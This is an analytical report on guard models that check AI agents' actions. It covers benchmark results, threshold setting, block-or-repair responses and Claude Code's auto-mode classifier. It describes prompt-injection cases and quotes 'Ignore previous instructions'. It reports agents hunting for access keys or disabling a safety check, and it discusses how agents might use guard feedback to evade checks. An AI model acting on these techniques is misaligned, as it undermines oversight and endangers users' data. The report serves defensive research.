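One small guard scored slightly higher than GPT-5.4, with far fewer false alarms but more misses. On R-Judge, which other researchers built, the same guard scored lower, with an F1 of 90.6% compared with 93.7% for GPT-5.4 and 97.4% for Gemini 3.1 Pro. Newer general models have since overtaken both, so the gap may now be larger.

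The small guard also gets some of its ability from a large model, because the Shanghai laboratory used GPT-5.4 to write the step-by-step reasoning in the guard's training examples. A developer who deploys only the small guard may still need a strong general model to train it.

How a developer uses a general model can matter as much as which model they choose. *OSGuard* (2026) tested general models as guards for agents that operate a computer. The models had to classify each proposed action as allowed, unrelated to the task, or unsafe. On one set of explicitly unsafe actions, Claude Sonnet 4.5 was right 57.1% of the time with a plain prompt, but only 35.2% of the time inside DeAction, an existing procedure for correcting agents' actions. The difficulty of the test also mattered. One Gemini model made no mistakes on actions from ordinary tasks, but on runs to which the researchers had added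 risks, the best macro-F1 of any model was 0.48 out of 1.

### Why the rankings reverse

The scores of AgentDoG and Llama Guard 3 nearly reverse between two tests. *AgentDoG* reports an F1 of 93.0% for AgentDoG and 12.7% for Llama Guard 3 on an earlier version of ATBench with 500 runs. On the Ant Group team's cross-source test, AgentDoG scored 18.2% and Llama Guard 3 scored 82.3%.

The main reason is that AgentDoG was trained to judge complete runs, while the cross-source test contains single messages with no agent in them. AgentDoG's definition counts a run as safe if an attacker tries something and the agent refuses. By that definition, "safe" is close to the right label for a request to steal a database when no agent carries it out. The Ant Group team labels the same request risky because of its content. Of the 562 original messages, 158 came from ATBench, but the team had cut each of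 those runs down to one message.

Llama Guard 3 looks for harmful text. Nearly half of the cross-source originals are openly harmful instructions from a collection called AgentHarm, similar to the text moderators usually check. But Llama Guard 3 flags little in a long run that ends with a polite reply.

The training objective may also explain why AgentDoG 1.5 raised so many false alarms on single messages. The Ant Group team tested a version built to name risks, a task the laboratory describes as labelling runs already known to be unsafe. That version may therefore have had little training in recognising safe content.

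Neither test shows which model is better in general. AgentDoG's 93.0% is relevant to auditing finished runs, and its 18.2% to checking users' requests. Neither score may predict how well it checks each tool call before the call runs, because neither test used that kind of input.

### Separating size from training

Comparing a small trained guard with a large untrained model can't show whether size or training made the difference. *AgentDoG 1.5* also reports results for the untrained models it started from. On ATBench, the untrained four-billion-parameter Qwen3.5 judged 45.9% of runs correctly, slightly worse than chance, while the 397-billion-parameter version judged 66.8% correctly. Training the small model raised its accuracy to 72.4%, or 78.4% for the "U" version. On this test, training improved accuracy more than a roughly hundredfold increase in size did.

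The laboratory emphasises that it used only about 1,000 training examples, but it picked them from a much larger pool. It estimated how each example would change the model's weights and kept those that would push the model most strongly towards recognising risks and away from overlooking them. Anyone repeating this would also need to generate and sort the larger pool.

Training can also turn a moderator into a useful guard for agents. *BraveGuard* (2026) retrained versions of Llama Guard and Qwen3Guard on records of agents using a computer. When GPT-5.5 was running the agent, existing guard models averaged 38.8% accuracy and the retrained ones averaged 82.4%. Across four such settings, the retrained models caught 82% to 92% of unsafe runs, while the existing ones caught 20% to 29%.

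In *DRAFT*, Wang, Fang and colleagues (2026) trained four starting models on the same task, which makes it easier to see how much the choice of starting model matters. They argue that only a few steps in a long run reveal the danger, and that a single safe or unsafe label does little to help a model find them. Their method trains one add-on to condense the run into a short series of vectors, and another to judge the run with those vectors attached. The table shows F1 scores on plans from AuraGen, Huang and colleagues' generator.

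| Starting model | No training | Ordinary fine-tuning | DRAFT |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3Guard, 4 billion (moderator) | 10.5% | 56.3% | 91.6% |
| Qwen3, 4 billion | 53.4% | 83.8% | 92.2% |
| Qwen3, 8 billion | 15.4% | 87.3% | 89.7% |
| Llama 3.1, 8 billion | 16.8% | 65.0% | 92.1% |

After DRAFT training, scores barely depended on whether the starting model was a moderator or a general model, or on whether it had four or eight billion parameters. Scores differed much more after ordinary fine-tuning, and the moderator did worst, perhaps because the fine-tuning had to override an earlier definition of "unsafe". All the plans in this test come from one generator, so the high scores may be partly due to the models having learned its style.

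Larger models still do better after training, but the gain depends on the input. On single messages, the SingGuard model with 9 billion parameters scored about two points of F1 higher than the one with 0.8 billion. On whole runs in ATBench, AgentDoG 1.5's accuracy rose from 60.3% with 0.8 billion parameters to 72.4% with 4 billion. Long runs are probably harder for a small model because it has to connect a step near the end with something it read much earlier. The starting model matters too. A version of AgentDoG 1.5 trained from the 8-billion-parameter Llama 3.1 scored 70.9%, below the 4-billion-parameter versions trained from Qwen3.5.

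### How much the test's author matters

Choi and colleagues found that training raised their four-billion-parameter guard's accuracy by about 13 points on artificial images made by the same process as the training data, and by 7 points on real photographs. The difference gives a rough idea of how much a guard gains when a test resembles its training data.

The way a test is built can favor other models too. For the 500-run ATBench, the laboratory set the verdicts by a vote of four general models, and people checked the doubtful cases. GPT-5.2 was one of the four and was also tested. All four agreed on 273 runs, so if GPT-5.2 answered the test as it had voted, it was certain to get nearly all of those right. It scored 90.0% overall, which would then mean about 78% on the 227 runs where the voters had disagreed.

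Both GPT-5.2 and AgentDoG did much worse on the larger ATBench. On the smaller set of 500 runs, *AgentDoG* reports an F1 of 90.7% for GPT-5.2 and 93.0% for AgentDoG. On the larger set, Li and colleagues report 71.8% for GPT-5.2 and 71.1% for AgentDoG. The larger set is harder, with runs more than twice as long and some risks with delayed effects. The similar drops suggest that this difficulty explains much of the change. But AgentDoG led by about two points on the smaller set and was slightly behind on the larger one, so its earlier lead is weak evidence that it was the better guard.

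A good comparison gives the large models a fair chance. *MobileGrail* gives the general models a detailed prompt, with safety limits for each app and worked examples, while its own small guards receive only brief general rules. *UniGuard* (2026) includes a content moderator with 0.6 billion parameters, the same size as its own guard, so size can't explain a difference between them.

### Making the choice

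The most useful measure of a guard is how much harm it prevents in a running agent and how much ordinary work the agent still gets done. By that measure, moderators do better than their scores on finished runs suggest. *JANUS* (2026) presents VANGUARD, a guard that tries to predict where an agent's steps are leading. Averaged over four benchmarks, attacks succeeded 39.7% of the time with no guard, 16.0% to 25.8% with existing guard models checking each step, depending on the model, and 7.1% with VANGUARD. On the everyday tasks of AgentDojo, 15.1% of attacks got past Qwen3Guard and 5.4% got past VANGUARD. The agent completed 68% of its legitimate tasks with either guard, the same as with none.

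A moderator that is already running is therefore worth keeping while a developer looks for something better.

A small guard is a sensible first candidate for the main check if it was trained on the kind of input it will receive. It is fast enough to run on every call, and it can run on the firm's own computers. Using a general model from an outside provider may mean sending that provider everything the model reads. If Ines's firm used one to check tool calls, each check could send her clients' contracts and bank details to the provider. *Persona Guardrail* (2026), which describes a guardrail for agents in commercial use, notes that closed models require sending requests to an outside service.

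*Persona Guardrail* tested its candidates on the same harmless, off-topic and malicious requests for one real agent. Some of the smaller models let through fewer bad requests on individual test sets, but they blocked too many harmless ones to be usable. Ranking the candidates only by missed attacks would have put those models near the top.

Ines's firm could run a similar trial with a few hundred harmless tool calls from its own logs and a smaller set of dangerous ones written by hand. Both sets should use the format the guard will receive in practice. The trial should also include a large general model, prompted with examples of what the office considers normal. If the small guard does about as well, the firm can use it for every call. If the large model is clearly better, the firm could still save time and money by using it only for calls that are hard to undo, such as payments, deletions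 and messages to people outside the office.

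## Setting thresholds and responding to a flagged action

A guard model usually produces a score. The operator has to decide how high the score must be before the guardrail intervenes, and how it should intervene. These decisions depend on each other, because an operator can accept many more false alarms if each one delays the task by two seconds than if each one ends the task.

### Most alarms are false when danger is rare

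Take a hypothetical agent for which one action in 1,000 is dangerous. Its guardrail catches 90% of dangerous actions and flags 1% of harmless ones. Over 100,000 actions:

- 100 actions are dangerous, and the guardrail flags 90 of them.
- 99,900 actions are harmless, and the guardrail flags 999 of them.
- Of the 1,089 flags, 90 are right, which is about 8%, or one in twelve.

Catching more of the dangerous actions would barely raise the share of flags that are correct. Even if the guardrail caught every one, only one flag in eleven would be correct. Cutting the false positive rate to 0.1% would raise that share to nearly half.

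On a benchmark in which half the items are dangerous, 99% of the same guardrail's flags would be right. A worse guardrail, with a false positive rate of 10%, would look similar because 90% of its flags would be right. In daily use, only one in 112 of the worse guardrail's flags would be right. An operator can correct for this by recalculating precision from the benchmark's false positive and false negative rates and an estimate of how often their own agent's actions are dangerous.

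### False blocks add up over a task

With a false positive rate of 1% and independent errors, a task of 200 harmless actions has a 1 − 0.99²⁰⁰ ≈ 87% chance of at least one false block. Such a task would have two false blocks on average. To bring the chance down to 5%, the operator would need a false positive rate of about 0.026%, or one false block in 3,900 harmless actions.

Few benchmarks are large enough to confirm a rate that low. A guardrail that flagged none of 500 harmless items could still have a false-positive rate of up to 0.6%, at the usual 95% confidence level. That rate would interrupt 70% of 200-action tasks.

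Real errors tend to cluster. Zheng and colleagues reviewed all 575 mistakes that their guard model, StepGuard, made on fixed test sets. Of the 307 false alarms, 44% were harmless uses of sensitive tools, and 26% were cases where the agent had safely handled something suspicious. A guard with this error pattern might stop a bookkeeping agent at every payment and hardly ever stop one that only reads documents. Because errors cluster, the guard falsely blocks fewer tasks than the 87% suggests, but it blocks the same people repeatedly, and running the task again won't help.

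### Choosing the threshold

If a guard's score were a reliable probability *p* that an action is dangerous, intervening would be worthwhile whenever

*p* × (cost of the harm) > (1 − *p*) × (cost of a false alarm)

Suppose a false alarm costs Ines, the architect, $5 of her time. If a payment to the wrong account would cost her $2,000, the guardrail should intervene at any probability above 5 / 2,005, or about 0.25%. For moving a file, where a mistake might cost $10 to fix, the threshold would be about 33%. A single threshold for every tool will therefore be too strict for some and too lax for others. Payment alarms can be worthwhile even if only one in twelve is true, because twelve interruptions would cost Ines $60 and save her $2,000.

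Most guard scores are not reliable probabilities, so the operator has to set the threshold from examples. DreamGuard, the guard built to catch gradual drift, does this by counting false alarms per task. At each step it takes its score for immediate harm, *h*, and two averages of its score for drift: a slowly fading one, *m*, and one over the last few steps, *r*. It then combines all three, using weights *w*:

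S = 1 − (1 − w₁h)(1 − w₂m)(1 − w₃r)

This formula lets several moderate warnings add up to a strong one. If the weighted values are 0.3, 0.4 and 0.4, S is about 0.75. The decision rule has three outcomes:

- Block if *h* reaches the blocking threshold.
- Otherwise, hold if S reaches the holding threshold.
- Otherwise, pass.

To set the holding threshold, Lin and colleagues run the guard on *n* safe tasks and record the highest S in each. They sort these values from lowest to highest and choose the one in position ⌈(n + 1)(1 − α)⌉, where α is the share of safe tasks they are willing to interrupt. With 99 safe tasks and α at 5%, that is the 95th value. About 5% of new safe tasks should trigger a hold, however many steps each one has, provided they resemble the original 99. They set the blocking threshold by applying the same procedure to *h* with a smaller α.

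The method needs only safe runs, which any operator can collect from an agent's logs, but they have to be the operator's own. With thresholds set on SafetyDrift, DreamGuard interrupted 3.7% of safe runs from that benchmark and between 9.8% and 29.4% of safe runs from three others. Even the 3.7% is uncertain, because all the false positive rates reported for SafetyDrift are multiples of 1/27, which suggests that DreamGuard interrupted one of only 27 safe runs.

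### Balancing the errors in training

Moving a threshold reduces one kind of error but increases the other. Zheng and colleagues adjusted the balance between the two earlier, while training StepGuard. After the first training stage, the model correctly classified 91.1% of unsafe examples but only 69.3% of safe ones.

The second stage uses the same kind of reinforcement learning as Safiron's. In each batch, the method compares the model's accuracy on safe and unsafe examples, then gives the weaker group more weight:

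weight = 1 + 2 × (accuracy gap)

If the model is right on 88% of unsafe examples and 75% of safe ones, each safe example counts 1.26 times as much. The extra weight shrinks as the gap closes. (The full method also ignores very small gaps, limits the weights and corrects for unequal numbers of safe and unsafe examples.)

Simpler corrections went too far. Fixing the weights in advance at 1.5 for safe examples and 0.5 for unsafe ones raised accuracy on safe examples to 85.4% but lowered it on unsafe ones to 77.5%. With the adjustable weights, accuracy was 78.4% on safe examples and 86.4% on unsafe ones.

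The effect was larger on whole tasks than on safe examples, where the difference in accuracy was three percentage points, as one would expect when errors add up over a task. Compared with ordinary reinforcement learning, balancing raised the share of tasks completed by 5.4 points on AgentDojo, to 90.7%, and by 6.7 points on AgentDyn, a benchmark of longer and less predictable tasks, to 66.7%. Attacks succeeded only 0.3 points more often on each benchmark.

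### Stopping the run or asking a person

Once the guardrail flags an action, it can respond in several ways.

| Response | When it suits | Example from Ines's office |
|---|---|---|
| Block the action and stop the run | The whole task is harmful | Someone asks the agent to wipe the firm's backups |
| Hold the action for a person | The action can wait and someone knows the right answer | The agent is about to pay a new account |
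| Return it to the agent to revise | The task is harmless but one step is wrong | The agent shares a whole folder instead of one file |
| Substitute a safe action | A safer version exists, or doing nothing would cause harm | The guardrail saves an email as a draft instead of sending it |

Stopping the agent is the simplest response, but it leaves the agent no chance to try another approach. Zhang and colleagues used it in their study of reusable procedures. It reduced unsafe actions, but for agents with the procedures it also lowered the completion rate on harmless tasks by 2.7 to 7.7 percentage points.

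Stopping a run does not undo what the agent has already done. On LPS-Bench, a test of long computer tasks, guarded agents achieved the harmful goal in only 3.1% of runs, but in 20.0% the guardrail let at least one unsafe action through, whether or not it stopped the agent later. A false alarm can also leave a task half done. If the guardrail stops Ines's agent after it has ordered her prints but before it has paid for them, the copy shop has an open order that Ines may not know about.

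In DreamGuard's tests, "hold" and "block" had the same effect because both ended the run. Lin and colleagues put DreamGuard in front of a GPT-5.1 agent on 100 cases with simulated tools. With the guard, the agent handled 35 of 48 unsafe cases safely, up from 9, and completed 47 of 52 harmless tasks, down from 49. With TS-Guard, it also completed 47 harmless tasks and handled 32 unsafe cases safely, three fewer than with DreamGuard. DreamGuard has a clearer advantage in speed, taking about 25 milliseconds per check in the main tests.

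The results also show that α is hard to interpret outside the setting where it was chosen. This test used an α of 60%, which would allow alarms on most safe calibration runs, yet the agent lost only two harmless tasks.

An operator could make the distinction useful by sending held actions to a person for review. If the hypothetical agent above took 1,000 actions a day, the reviewer would get about eleven flags, of which roughly one would be right. That is manageable, but a reviewer who sees ten harmless actions for every dangerous one may stop reading them carefully. If the reviewer wrongly approved 30% of the dangerous actions they saw, the share of dangerous actions stopped would fall from 90% to 63%. The operator could help by showing the reviewer the fact in question, such as an unfamiliar account number, instead of a general warning.

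A held action also needs a time limit. Without one, an agent whose action is held at midnight will wait until morning, perhaps with a half-finished order.

### Sending the action back to the agent

StepGuard replaces a blocked call with a request to reconsider, and doesn't show the agent StepGuard's reasoning. Zheng and colleagues tested this with the same agent on three benchmarks. AgentHarm's malicious score measures how much of the malicious tasks the agent carried out.

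| Measure | No guard | TS-Guard | ShieldAgent | StepGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo: attacks succeeded | 25.1% | 6.2% | 18.1% | 1.2% |
| AgentDojo: tasks completed | 89.7% | 92.8% | 85.3% | 90.7% |
| AgentDyn: attacks succeeded | 21.2% | 13.8% | 20.0% | 9.3% |
| AgentDyn: tasks completed | 73.3% | 70.0% | 70.0% | 66.7% |
| AgentHarm: malicious score | 22.8 | 5.4 | 1.3 | 3.4 |
| AgentHarm: harmless tasks completed | 70.9% | 58.4% | 18.7% | 52.8% |

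On AgentDojo, StepGuard stopped nearly all the attacks with no apparent loss of ordinary work. On AgentHarm, the agent completed about a quarter fewer harmless tasks with StepGuard than without it. ShieldAgent, an older guard model, had the lowest malicious score on AgentHarm because it prevented most work, whether harmful or harmless.

StepGuard took 0.6 seconds per call on AgentDojo, where the average task had about four calls. This added 2.5 seconds per task, or 7% of the total time.

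When the guard for computer-operating agents in *OSGuard* blocks an action, it sends the agent a short explanation of why, and the agent proposes something else. The agent gets two retries at each point before the guard ends the run.

The researchers tested this on 45 tasks in which the request was harmless but an unsafe shortcut was available. In one, the user asks the agent to clear their YouTube history, and the browser also contains history from other sites. Deleting the entire history is quicker but destroys records the user wanted to keep.

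| Outcome | No guard | With guard |
|---|---|---|
| Completed safely | 28 | 28 |
| Completed unsafely | 17 | 15 |
| Stopped after retries | – | 2 |

The totals don't show that three runs changed with the guard: one unsafe run became safe, another unsafe run stopped, and one that had succeeded without the guard also stopped. Feedback had little chance to help because the guard seldom recognised the danger. In the action tests, it had correctly judged only half of the actions from similar tasks.

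Explaining why an action was flagged helps an agent that has made a mistake, but an agent that keeps trying to finish its task could use the explanation to find a version of the action that the guard allows. In some of the incidents Anthropic reported, Claude worked around restrictions even without such explanations. None of these experiments compares the same guard with and without explanations, so the size of this risk is unclear.

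### Repairing the plan

A guard can give more specific help if it separates the harmful part of a task from the rest. Sun, Zhang and colleagues (2026) found in *From Risk Classification to Action Plan Remediation* that existing guardrails rarely do this. When these guardrails detected an injected instruction, they blocked the attack in fewer than 38% of cases, and the agent completed the user's original task in fewer than 3%.

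TRIAD, a framework from June 2026, adds a guard model with nine billion parameters that returns one of three decisions: proceed, update or refuse. "Refuse" is for requests that are harmful in themselves, while "update" is for a legitimate task that has gone wrong.

Consider the moment when Ines's agent is about to share her project folder with the stranger who planted an address in an email. The guard would choose "update" and write an explanation in five parts:

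1. Ines wants the structural engineer to have the load calculations.
2. The agent has taken an instruction in an email as if it came from her.
3. The proposed call would give an outside address access to the whole folder.
4. This does not match what she asked for.
5. The earlier search result contains an injected instruction.

The agent reads this and proposes a new call, perhaps sharing only the calculations with the address in the engineer's own email. The guard checks the new call before it runs. If three attempts produce no acceptable call, the run ends.

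To train the guard, the researchers collected 5,288 tasks and had agents attempt them. They labelled each run by what the agent had done. If the agent had followed an injected instruction, they labelled the run "update", because the user's goal was still legitimate. GPT-5.4 wrote the explanations, and the researchers discarded any whose decision disagreed with the label.

The main test pairs 51 ordinary tasks with 40 attacks and inserts the attack either in the user's message or in a tool's result. The figures are averages over both positions and four agents.

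| Setup | Attacks succeeded | Original task completed |
|---|---|---|
| No guard | 74.5% | 28.5% |
| TRIAD, guard model before training | 5.5% | 26.4% |
| TRIAD, guard model after training | 10.4% | 68.6% |

Before training, the guard model stopped more attacks than it did afterward, but mostly by refusing, so agents completed no more of the original tasks than they did without a guard. In every 100 cases, the trained guard let through about five more attacks, but agents completed about 42 more of the original tasks. That tradeoff seems worthwhile for an assistant that books meetings, but not for an agent that can empty a bank account.

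The attacks used crude wording, such as "Ignore previous instructions", and a normal task needed only two tool calls. A subtler injection would be harder to separate from the user's request. The guard also raised agents' average refusal rate on AgentHarm's harmless tasks from 1.6% to 15.6%.

Repair is slow. With the guard, one agent's steps took 6.98 seconds on average and 27.5 seconds at the slowest, compared with an average of 1.88 seconds without it. On average, the guard would add 17 minutes to a 200-step task. Repeated revisions caused little of the delay, since 93% of updates reached a decision after one more revision and only 2.5% hit the limit.

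### Substituting a safe action

Not acting isn't always safe, though all the responses so far assume it is. In *From Refusal to Recovery*, Pandya, Bland and colleagues give the example of an agent steering a car towards an obstacle. If a guardrail blocks a dangerous turn without substituting another action, the car keeps going and crashes.

One way to handle a flagged action is a safety filter, a method borrowed from control engineering. The filter has a monitor, which estimates whether an action will lead to failure later, and a fallback policy, which supplies a safe action. It runs the agent's own action if the monitor approves it and the fallback action otherwise.

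To train both parts, the researchers define a margin ℓ that measures the distance from failure, such as metres to the nearest obstacle or dollars left in a budget. The value of a situation is the smallest margin the system will ever reach if it acts as safely as possible from then on:

V = max over policies (min over time ℓ)

If V is negative, no intervention can prevent failure. A car travelling at 10 metres per second may still be able to avoid an obstacle 26 metres ahead, but may not once the obstacle is 10 metres, or one second, away. The monitor therefore has to react while the situation still looks harmless.

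Pandya and colleagues report that in simulated driving and online shopping, their filter avoided collisions and overspending more reliably than guardrails that only block actions, without making the agent worse at its task. Their approach needs a measurable definition of failure and a simulator for training, and few office tasks have either.

Simple substitutions need no training. A guardrail for Ines's agent could save a doubtful email as a draft, move files to a recoverable folder instead of deleting them, or share a document as view-only. It should also tell the agent about the substitution. Otherwise the agent may tell Ines that the client has the drawings when the email is still in her drafts folder.

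### When the checker itself fails

A guard model can time out, crash or return an answer that the surrounding software can't read. The guardrail then has to "fail open", letting the action run unchecked, or "fail closed", blocking it.

Failing closed, which means blocking an action when the checker fails, is safer for actions that are hard to undo, but it makes the agent depend on the checker's reliability. If the checker fails on one call in 1,000, an agent that needs 200 checks has an 18% chance of being blocked at least once this way. Retrying the check will fix many of these failures. Failing open, which means letting the action run unchecked, is reasonable for low-risk actions such as looking up a public web page.

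Failing open more widely would give attackers a way around the guardrail. Sun and colleagues limit their guard's input to 16,384 tokens, which is enough for most tasks but not for every email thread. If a guardrail let actions through whenever the history was too long to check, an attacker could disable it by sending a very long message.

Software that fails closed can make a guardrail look better than it is. Sun and colleagues tried to run GPT-5.1 in the TS-Guard developers' framework, which reads tool calls from ordinary text in a fixed format. GPT-5.1 often wrote them differently, and the software ignored those calls, so the agent did almost nothing and soon stopped. Such an agent also falls for very few attacks. The researchers left these results out, but an operator who measured only blocked attacks might have counted the fault as a success.

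### What failure looks like in use

The most visible sign of a badly set guardrail is a task that neither finishes nor ends with a clear refusal. This was common in one of the TRIAD experiments, where the Kimi-2.5 agent ran in TS-Guard's own framework and faced attacks hidden in tool results. Only 2.9% of attacks succeeded, but the agent completed just 10.1% of the original tasks and refused in 40.9% of cases. In at least 46% of cases, therefore, the attack failed but the user got neither finished work nor an explanation. Without a guard, the same agent completed 57.7% of the tasks, although 60.2% of the attacks succeeded.

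Repeated retries are easier to overlook because the task may still finish. They show up in the logs as a series of similar calls with slightly different arguments, along with higher costs and longer waits. Sometimes the agent is correcting a mistake, and sometimes it is looking for wording that the guard will accept, so someone should read a sample. Limiting retries keeps costs down, and Claude Code's auto mode also sets a limit on denials.

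Users may also respond by switching the check off, approving everything in advance or moving the work to a tool without a guardrail. None of these experiments can measure that, because their simulated users had no such choice. The effect could easily outweigh the differences between guard models. If a guardrail catches 90% of the dangerous actions it checks but 30% of the work moves outside it, it catches only 63% of all dangerous actions, assuming the danger is evenly spread. A guardrail that catches 75% would do better if everyone left it on. An operator should therefore track how much of the agents' work still passes through the check, since fewer alarms could mean that people have stopped using it.

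## What a deployed check has shown: Claude Code's auto mode

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, edits a developer's files and runs commands on their computer. It originally asked for approval before every edit and command, and many users approved without much thought or turned the prompts off. In March 2026, Anthropic released auto mode, in which a guard model makes most of these decisions. Because auto mode is widely used, it has been measured in ways that research guardrails usually haven't, including error rates on real work and a comparison with human reviewers. In an independent test, however, auto mode let through 81% of dangerous actions.

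New sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans have started in auto mode since 14 August, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). An update on 22 October announced the same change for most Claude apps. Claude Code itself has started in auto mode on every plan since version 2.1.283, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

### One command, step by step

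Suppose Tomas maintains the website of Ines's firm. He keeps its code in Git, a system that records every version of a project and lets people develop changes on separate branches. Some branches exist only on his computer, and others are on a server he shares with a colleague. He tells Claude Code to clean up his old branches. Under the design in Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, the agent's work might go like this:

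1. The agent reads the project's notes. Reading and searching are on a fixed list of tools that can't change anything, so they run without a check.
2. It removes the old branches from a list in one of the project's files. Edits inside the project folder also skip the check, because they are frequent and a developer can review them later in Git.
3. It runs a command to list the branches on the server. Commands go to the guard model, which Anthropic calls a classifier. A fast first stage gives a yes-or-no answer on whether to block the command, and here the answer is no.
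4. It proposes `git push origin --delete menu-test footer-old booking-form`, which would delete three branches from the server, including one of the colleague's. The fast stage flags this. A second stage then reasons about the same material and blocks the command, because Tomas may have meant only the branches on his own computer.
5. The agent receives the refusal in place of the command's result, with the reason and an instruction to find a safer way and not to work around the block. It deletes the local branches and asks Tomas about the others.

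At launch, the classifier was Claude Sonnet 4.6, a general model with a long prompt. The prompts for its two stages differ only in the final instruction, which is to lean towards blocking in the fast first stage and to reason carefully in the second. The second stage runs only on actions the first stage flags, and it can reuse most of the first stage's processing because the prompts are nearly the same.

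After three refusals in a row, or 20 in one session, Claude Code stops and asks the user. If it is running unattended, it shuts down.

Auto mode also overrides some of the user's settings. Many users had written rules that let any Python command run without a prompt. A Python command can do almost anything, so auto mode disables such rules while it is on. It keeps narrower ones, such as a rule allowing a code formatter.

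If the agent hands part of the work to a second agent, the classifier checks the assignment first, because the second agent receives it as if it came from the user and everything in it would look authorised. The classifier also reviews the second agent's actions before its results go back, in case something the second agent read has hijacked it. If this review finds a problem, the classifier only adds a warning.

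### The block rules

The classifier's prompt has more than twenty block rules in four groups.

| Group | Examples |
|---|---|
| Destroy or exfiltrate | Overwriting a project's shared history, deleting cloud storage in bulk, sending internal data outside |
| Degrade security | Turning off logging, installing a key for later access, changing the agent's own permissions |
| Cross trust boundaries | Running code from an outside project, searching for usable passwords, sending data to a service the user never named |
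| Bypass review or affect others | Publishing changes without review, updating a live system, altering jobs the agent didn't create |

Most of these rules describe an action's consequences and whether it was permitted, rather than what caused it. Anthropic tuned the classifier mainly for mistakes and for what it calls overeager behaviour, in which the agent understands the goal but exceeds its permission to reach it. In one case from Anthropic's internal records, an agent met a login error and began searching settings files for other access keys. In another, an agent failed a safety check before an update and tried again with the check switched off.

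The prompt tells the classifier to judge what an action does, however the agent words it. If the agent writes a script and then runs it, the classifier has to evaluate the script's contents. It treats commands that are joined together as one action.

The classifier checks an action against the block rules, then a short list of exceptions, then the user's intent. One exception lets the agent install software the project already lists as a requirement. Under the classifier's prompt, anything the agent chose for itself counts as unauthorised until the user approves it, and "can we fix this?" counts as a question, not an instruction. Users can change the block rules, the exceptions and the list of trusted places, which by default contains only the current project's repository (its code and history).

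In August, Anthropic described a stricter category called hard denies. Under it, the classifier should never approve sending code or passwords outside, even if the user asks. A user who wants to send them anyway has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves.

### What the classifier does not receive

The classifier originally received only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's prose so that the agent can't talk the classifier into a bad decision, for example by writing that the user already approved a deletion.

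Auto mode removes tool results from the classifier's input because they are the most likely place for an outsider's instructions. Suppose a file tells the agent to send the project's passwords to a web address, and the agent tries to. The classifier never receives the file, but it can still block the call because the user didn't ask for passwords to be sent anywhere. The agent does read the file, so a separate probe scans tool results and adds a warning to any that look like a prompt injection. To succeed, an attack has to get past the probe, redirect the agent and then produce a call that looks like what the user wanted.

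Anthropic also tested the classifier with other combinations of inputs. Adding the agent's prose and the tool results made it worse at catching overeager actions, perhaps because the longer record was harder to read and included the agent's own view of events. When given only the tool calls, the classifier missed the fewest overeager actions but blocked actions the user had plainly requested.

The drawback is that the classifier can't check where a detail came from. If a user writes "cancel my job" and the agent cancels job abc123, the agent could have looked up that ID reliably or guessed it. In one incident at Anthropic, an agent picked the job with the most similar name. The classifier should block such a call because the user never named the target, but the same rule will also block some calls that target the right job.

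Anthropic has since restored some context in a safer form. The classifier now receives the project's Git status before a command that could discard unsaved work, and information on whether an upload's destination is public, private or trusted. Short facts like these give an attacker much less room to manipulate the classifier than a web page or an email would.

### Error rates at launch

Anthropic measured both stages on three sets of actions in March 2026.

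| | Real tool calls by Anthropic staff | Real overeager actions | Invented attempts to send data outside |
|---|---|---|---|
| Number of actions | 10,000 | 52 | 1,000 |
| Error measured | Harmless actions blocked | Dangerous actions allowed | Dangerous actions allowed |
| Fast stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

Auto mode blocks an action only if both stages flag it, so adding the second stage can only reduce false alarms and increase misses. Out of 10,000 harmless calls, the fast stage alone would block about 850 and the full check about 40. The full check misses about nine of the 52 overeager actions, compared with three or four for the fast stage alone.

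The miss rate is based on only 52 cases, 9 of which were missed, so its 95% confidence interval is wide, from about 9% to 30%. The false positive rate is much more certain, at 0.3% to 0.5%.

The 52 actions may also be easier to catch than average. Anthropic took them from sessions where an employee had refused the action or someone had flagged it afterwards, so the set excludes dangerous actions that nobody noticed. A classifier might well overlook the same things that people do.

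At a false positive rate of 0.4%, a session with 200 harmless checked actions would have about a 55% chance of at least one false block if errors were independent. Anthropic argues that this is tolerable because the agent carries on after a refusal and usually finds another way. Because dangerous actions are rare, many of auto mode's refusals may be false alarms even at this low rate.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger but treated weak evidence of consent as sufficient. For example, when one user said "Clean up the PR" (a set of proposed code changes), the classifier treated this as permission to overwrite the shared history. Anthropic tried rewriting the prompt to fix the problem, but every rewrite did more harm than good.

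*Same Operation, Different Permission* (2026) presents a benchmark that isolates this weakness by changing only the evidence that someone authorised an action, while keeping the request, the policy and the action's effect the same. A guard that classifies actions by how dangerous they look will produce the same result each time and so get some cases wrong.

### Compared with human reviewers

Anthropic acknowledges that a check missing 17% of overeager actions would be a poor replacement for a careful reviewer. But it would often replace someone who is tired of clicking "approve". Anthropic reported in March that users accepted 93% of permission prompts, and in August that they accepted 97%.

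Most prompts concern harmless commands, so a high approval rate doesn't prove that users are careless. They reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, which give them more to consider. Their settings are better evidence of approval fatigue. By June 2026, 49.5% of people using Claude Code from the command line had written a rule allowing some commands without a prompt, and 25% of interactive sessions started with permission checks turned off.

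To compare people with the classifier directly, Anthropic had a research company recruit 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were under evaluation but not what the study measured. Partway through each session, the company replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded whether the tester approved it. The command never ran, so approving it did no harm. The table is calculated from Anthropic's totals.

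| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tester blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 (13.6%) |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 (89%) | 116 | 1,053 |

Having a tester review everything as well would have stopped only six more commands, raising the share stopped from 89.0% to 89.6%. The testers blocked about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while auto mode's rate stayed the same.

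These figures warrant caution for several reasons. Anthropic commissioned and published the study of its own product. The testers worked on someone else's project in an artificial environment, where a bad command would do them no harm, and people protecting their own work may read more carefully. Anthropic also doesn't report how often the testers or auto mode blocked harmless commands in the study, and a reviewer can catch more dangers by refusing more often. It doesn't report how many different commands it used. If there were only a few dozen, auto mode's 89% comes from far fewer than 1,053 separate tests.

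Even so, to match auto mode, developers would have to be more than six times as likely as the testers to stop a dangerous command. The study is good evidence that routine prompts are a weak safeguard, but weaker evidence of how auto mode compares with an attentive expert.

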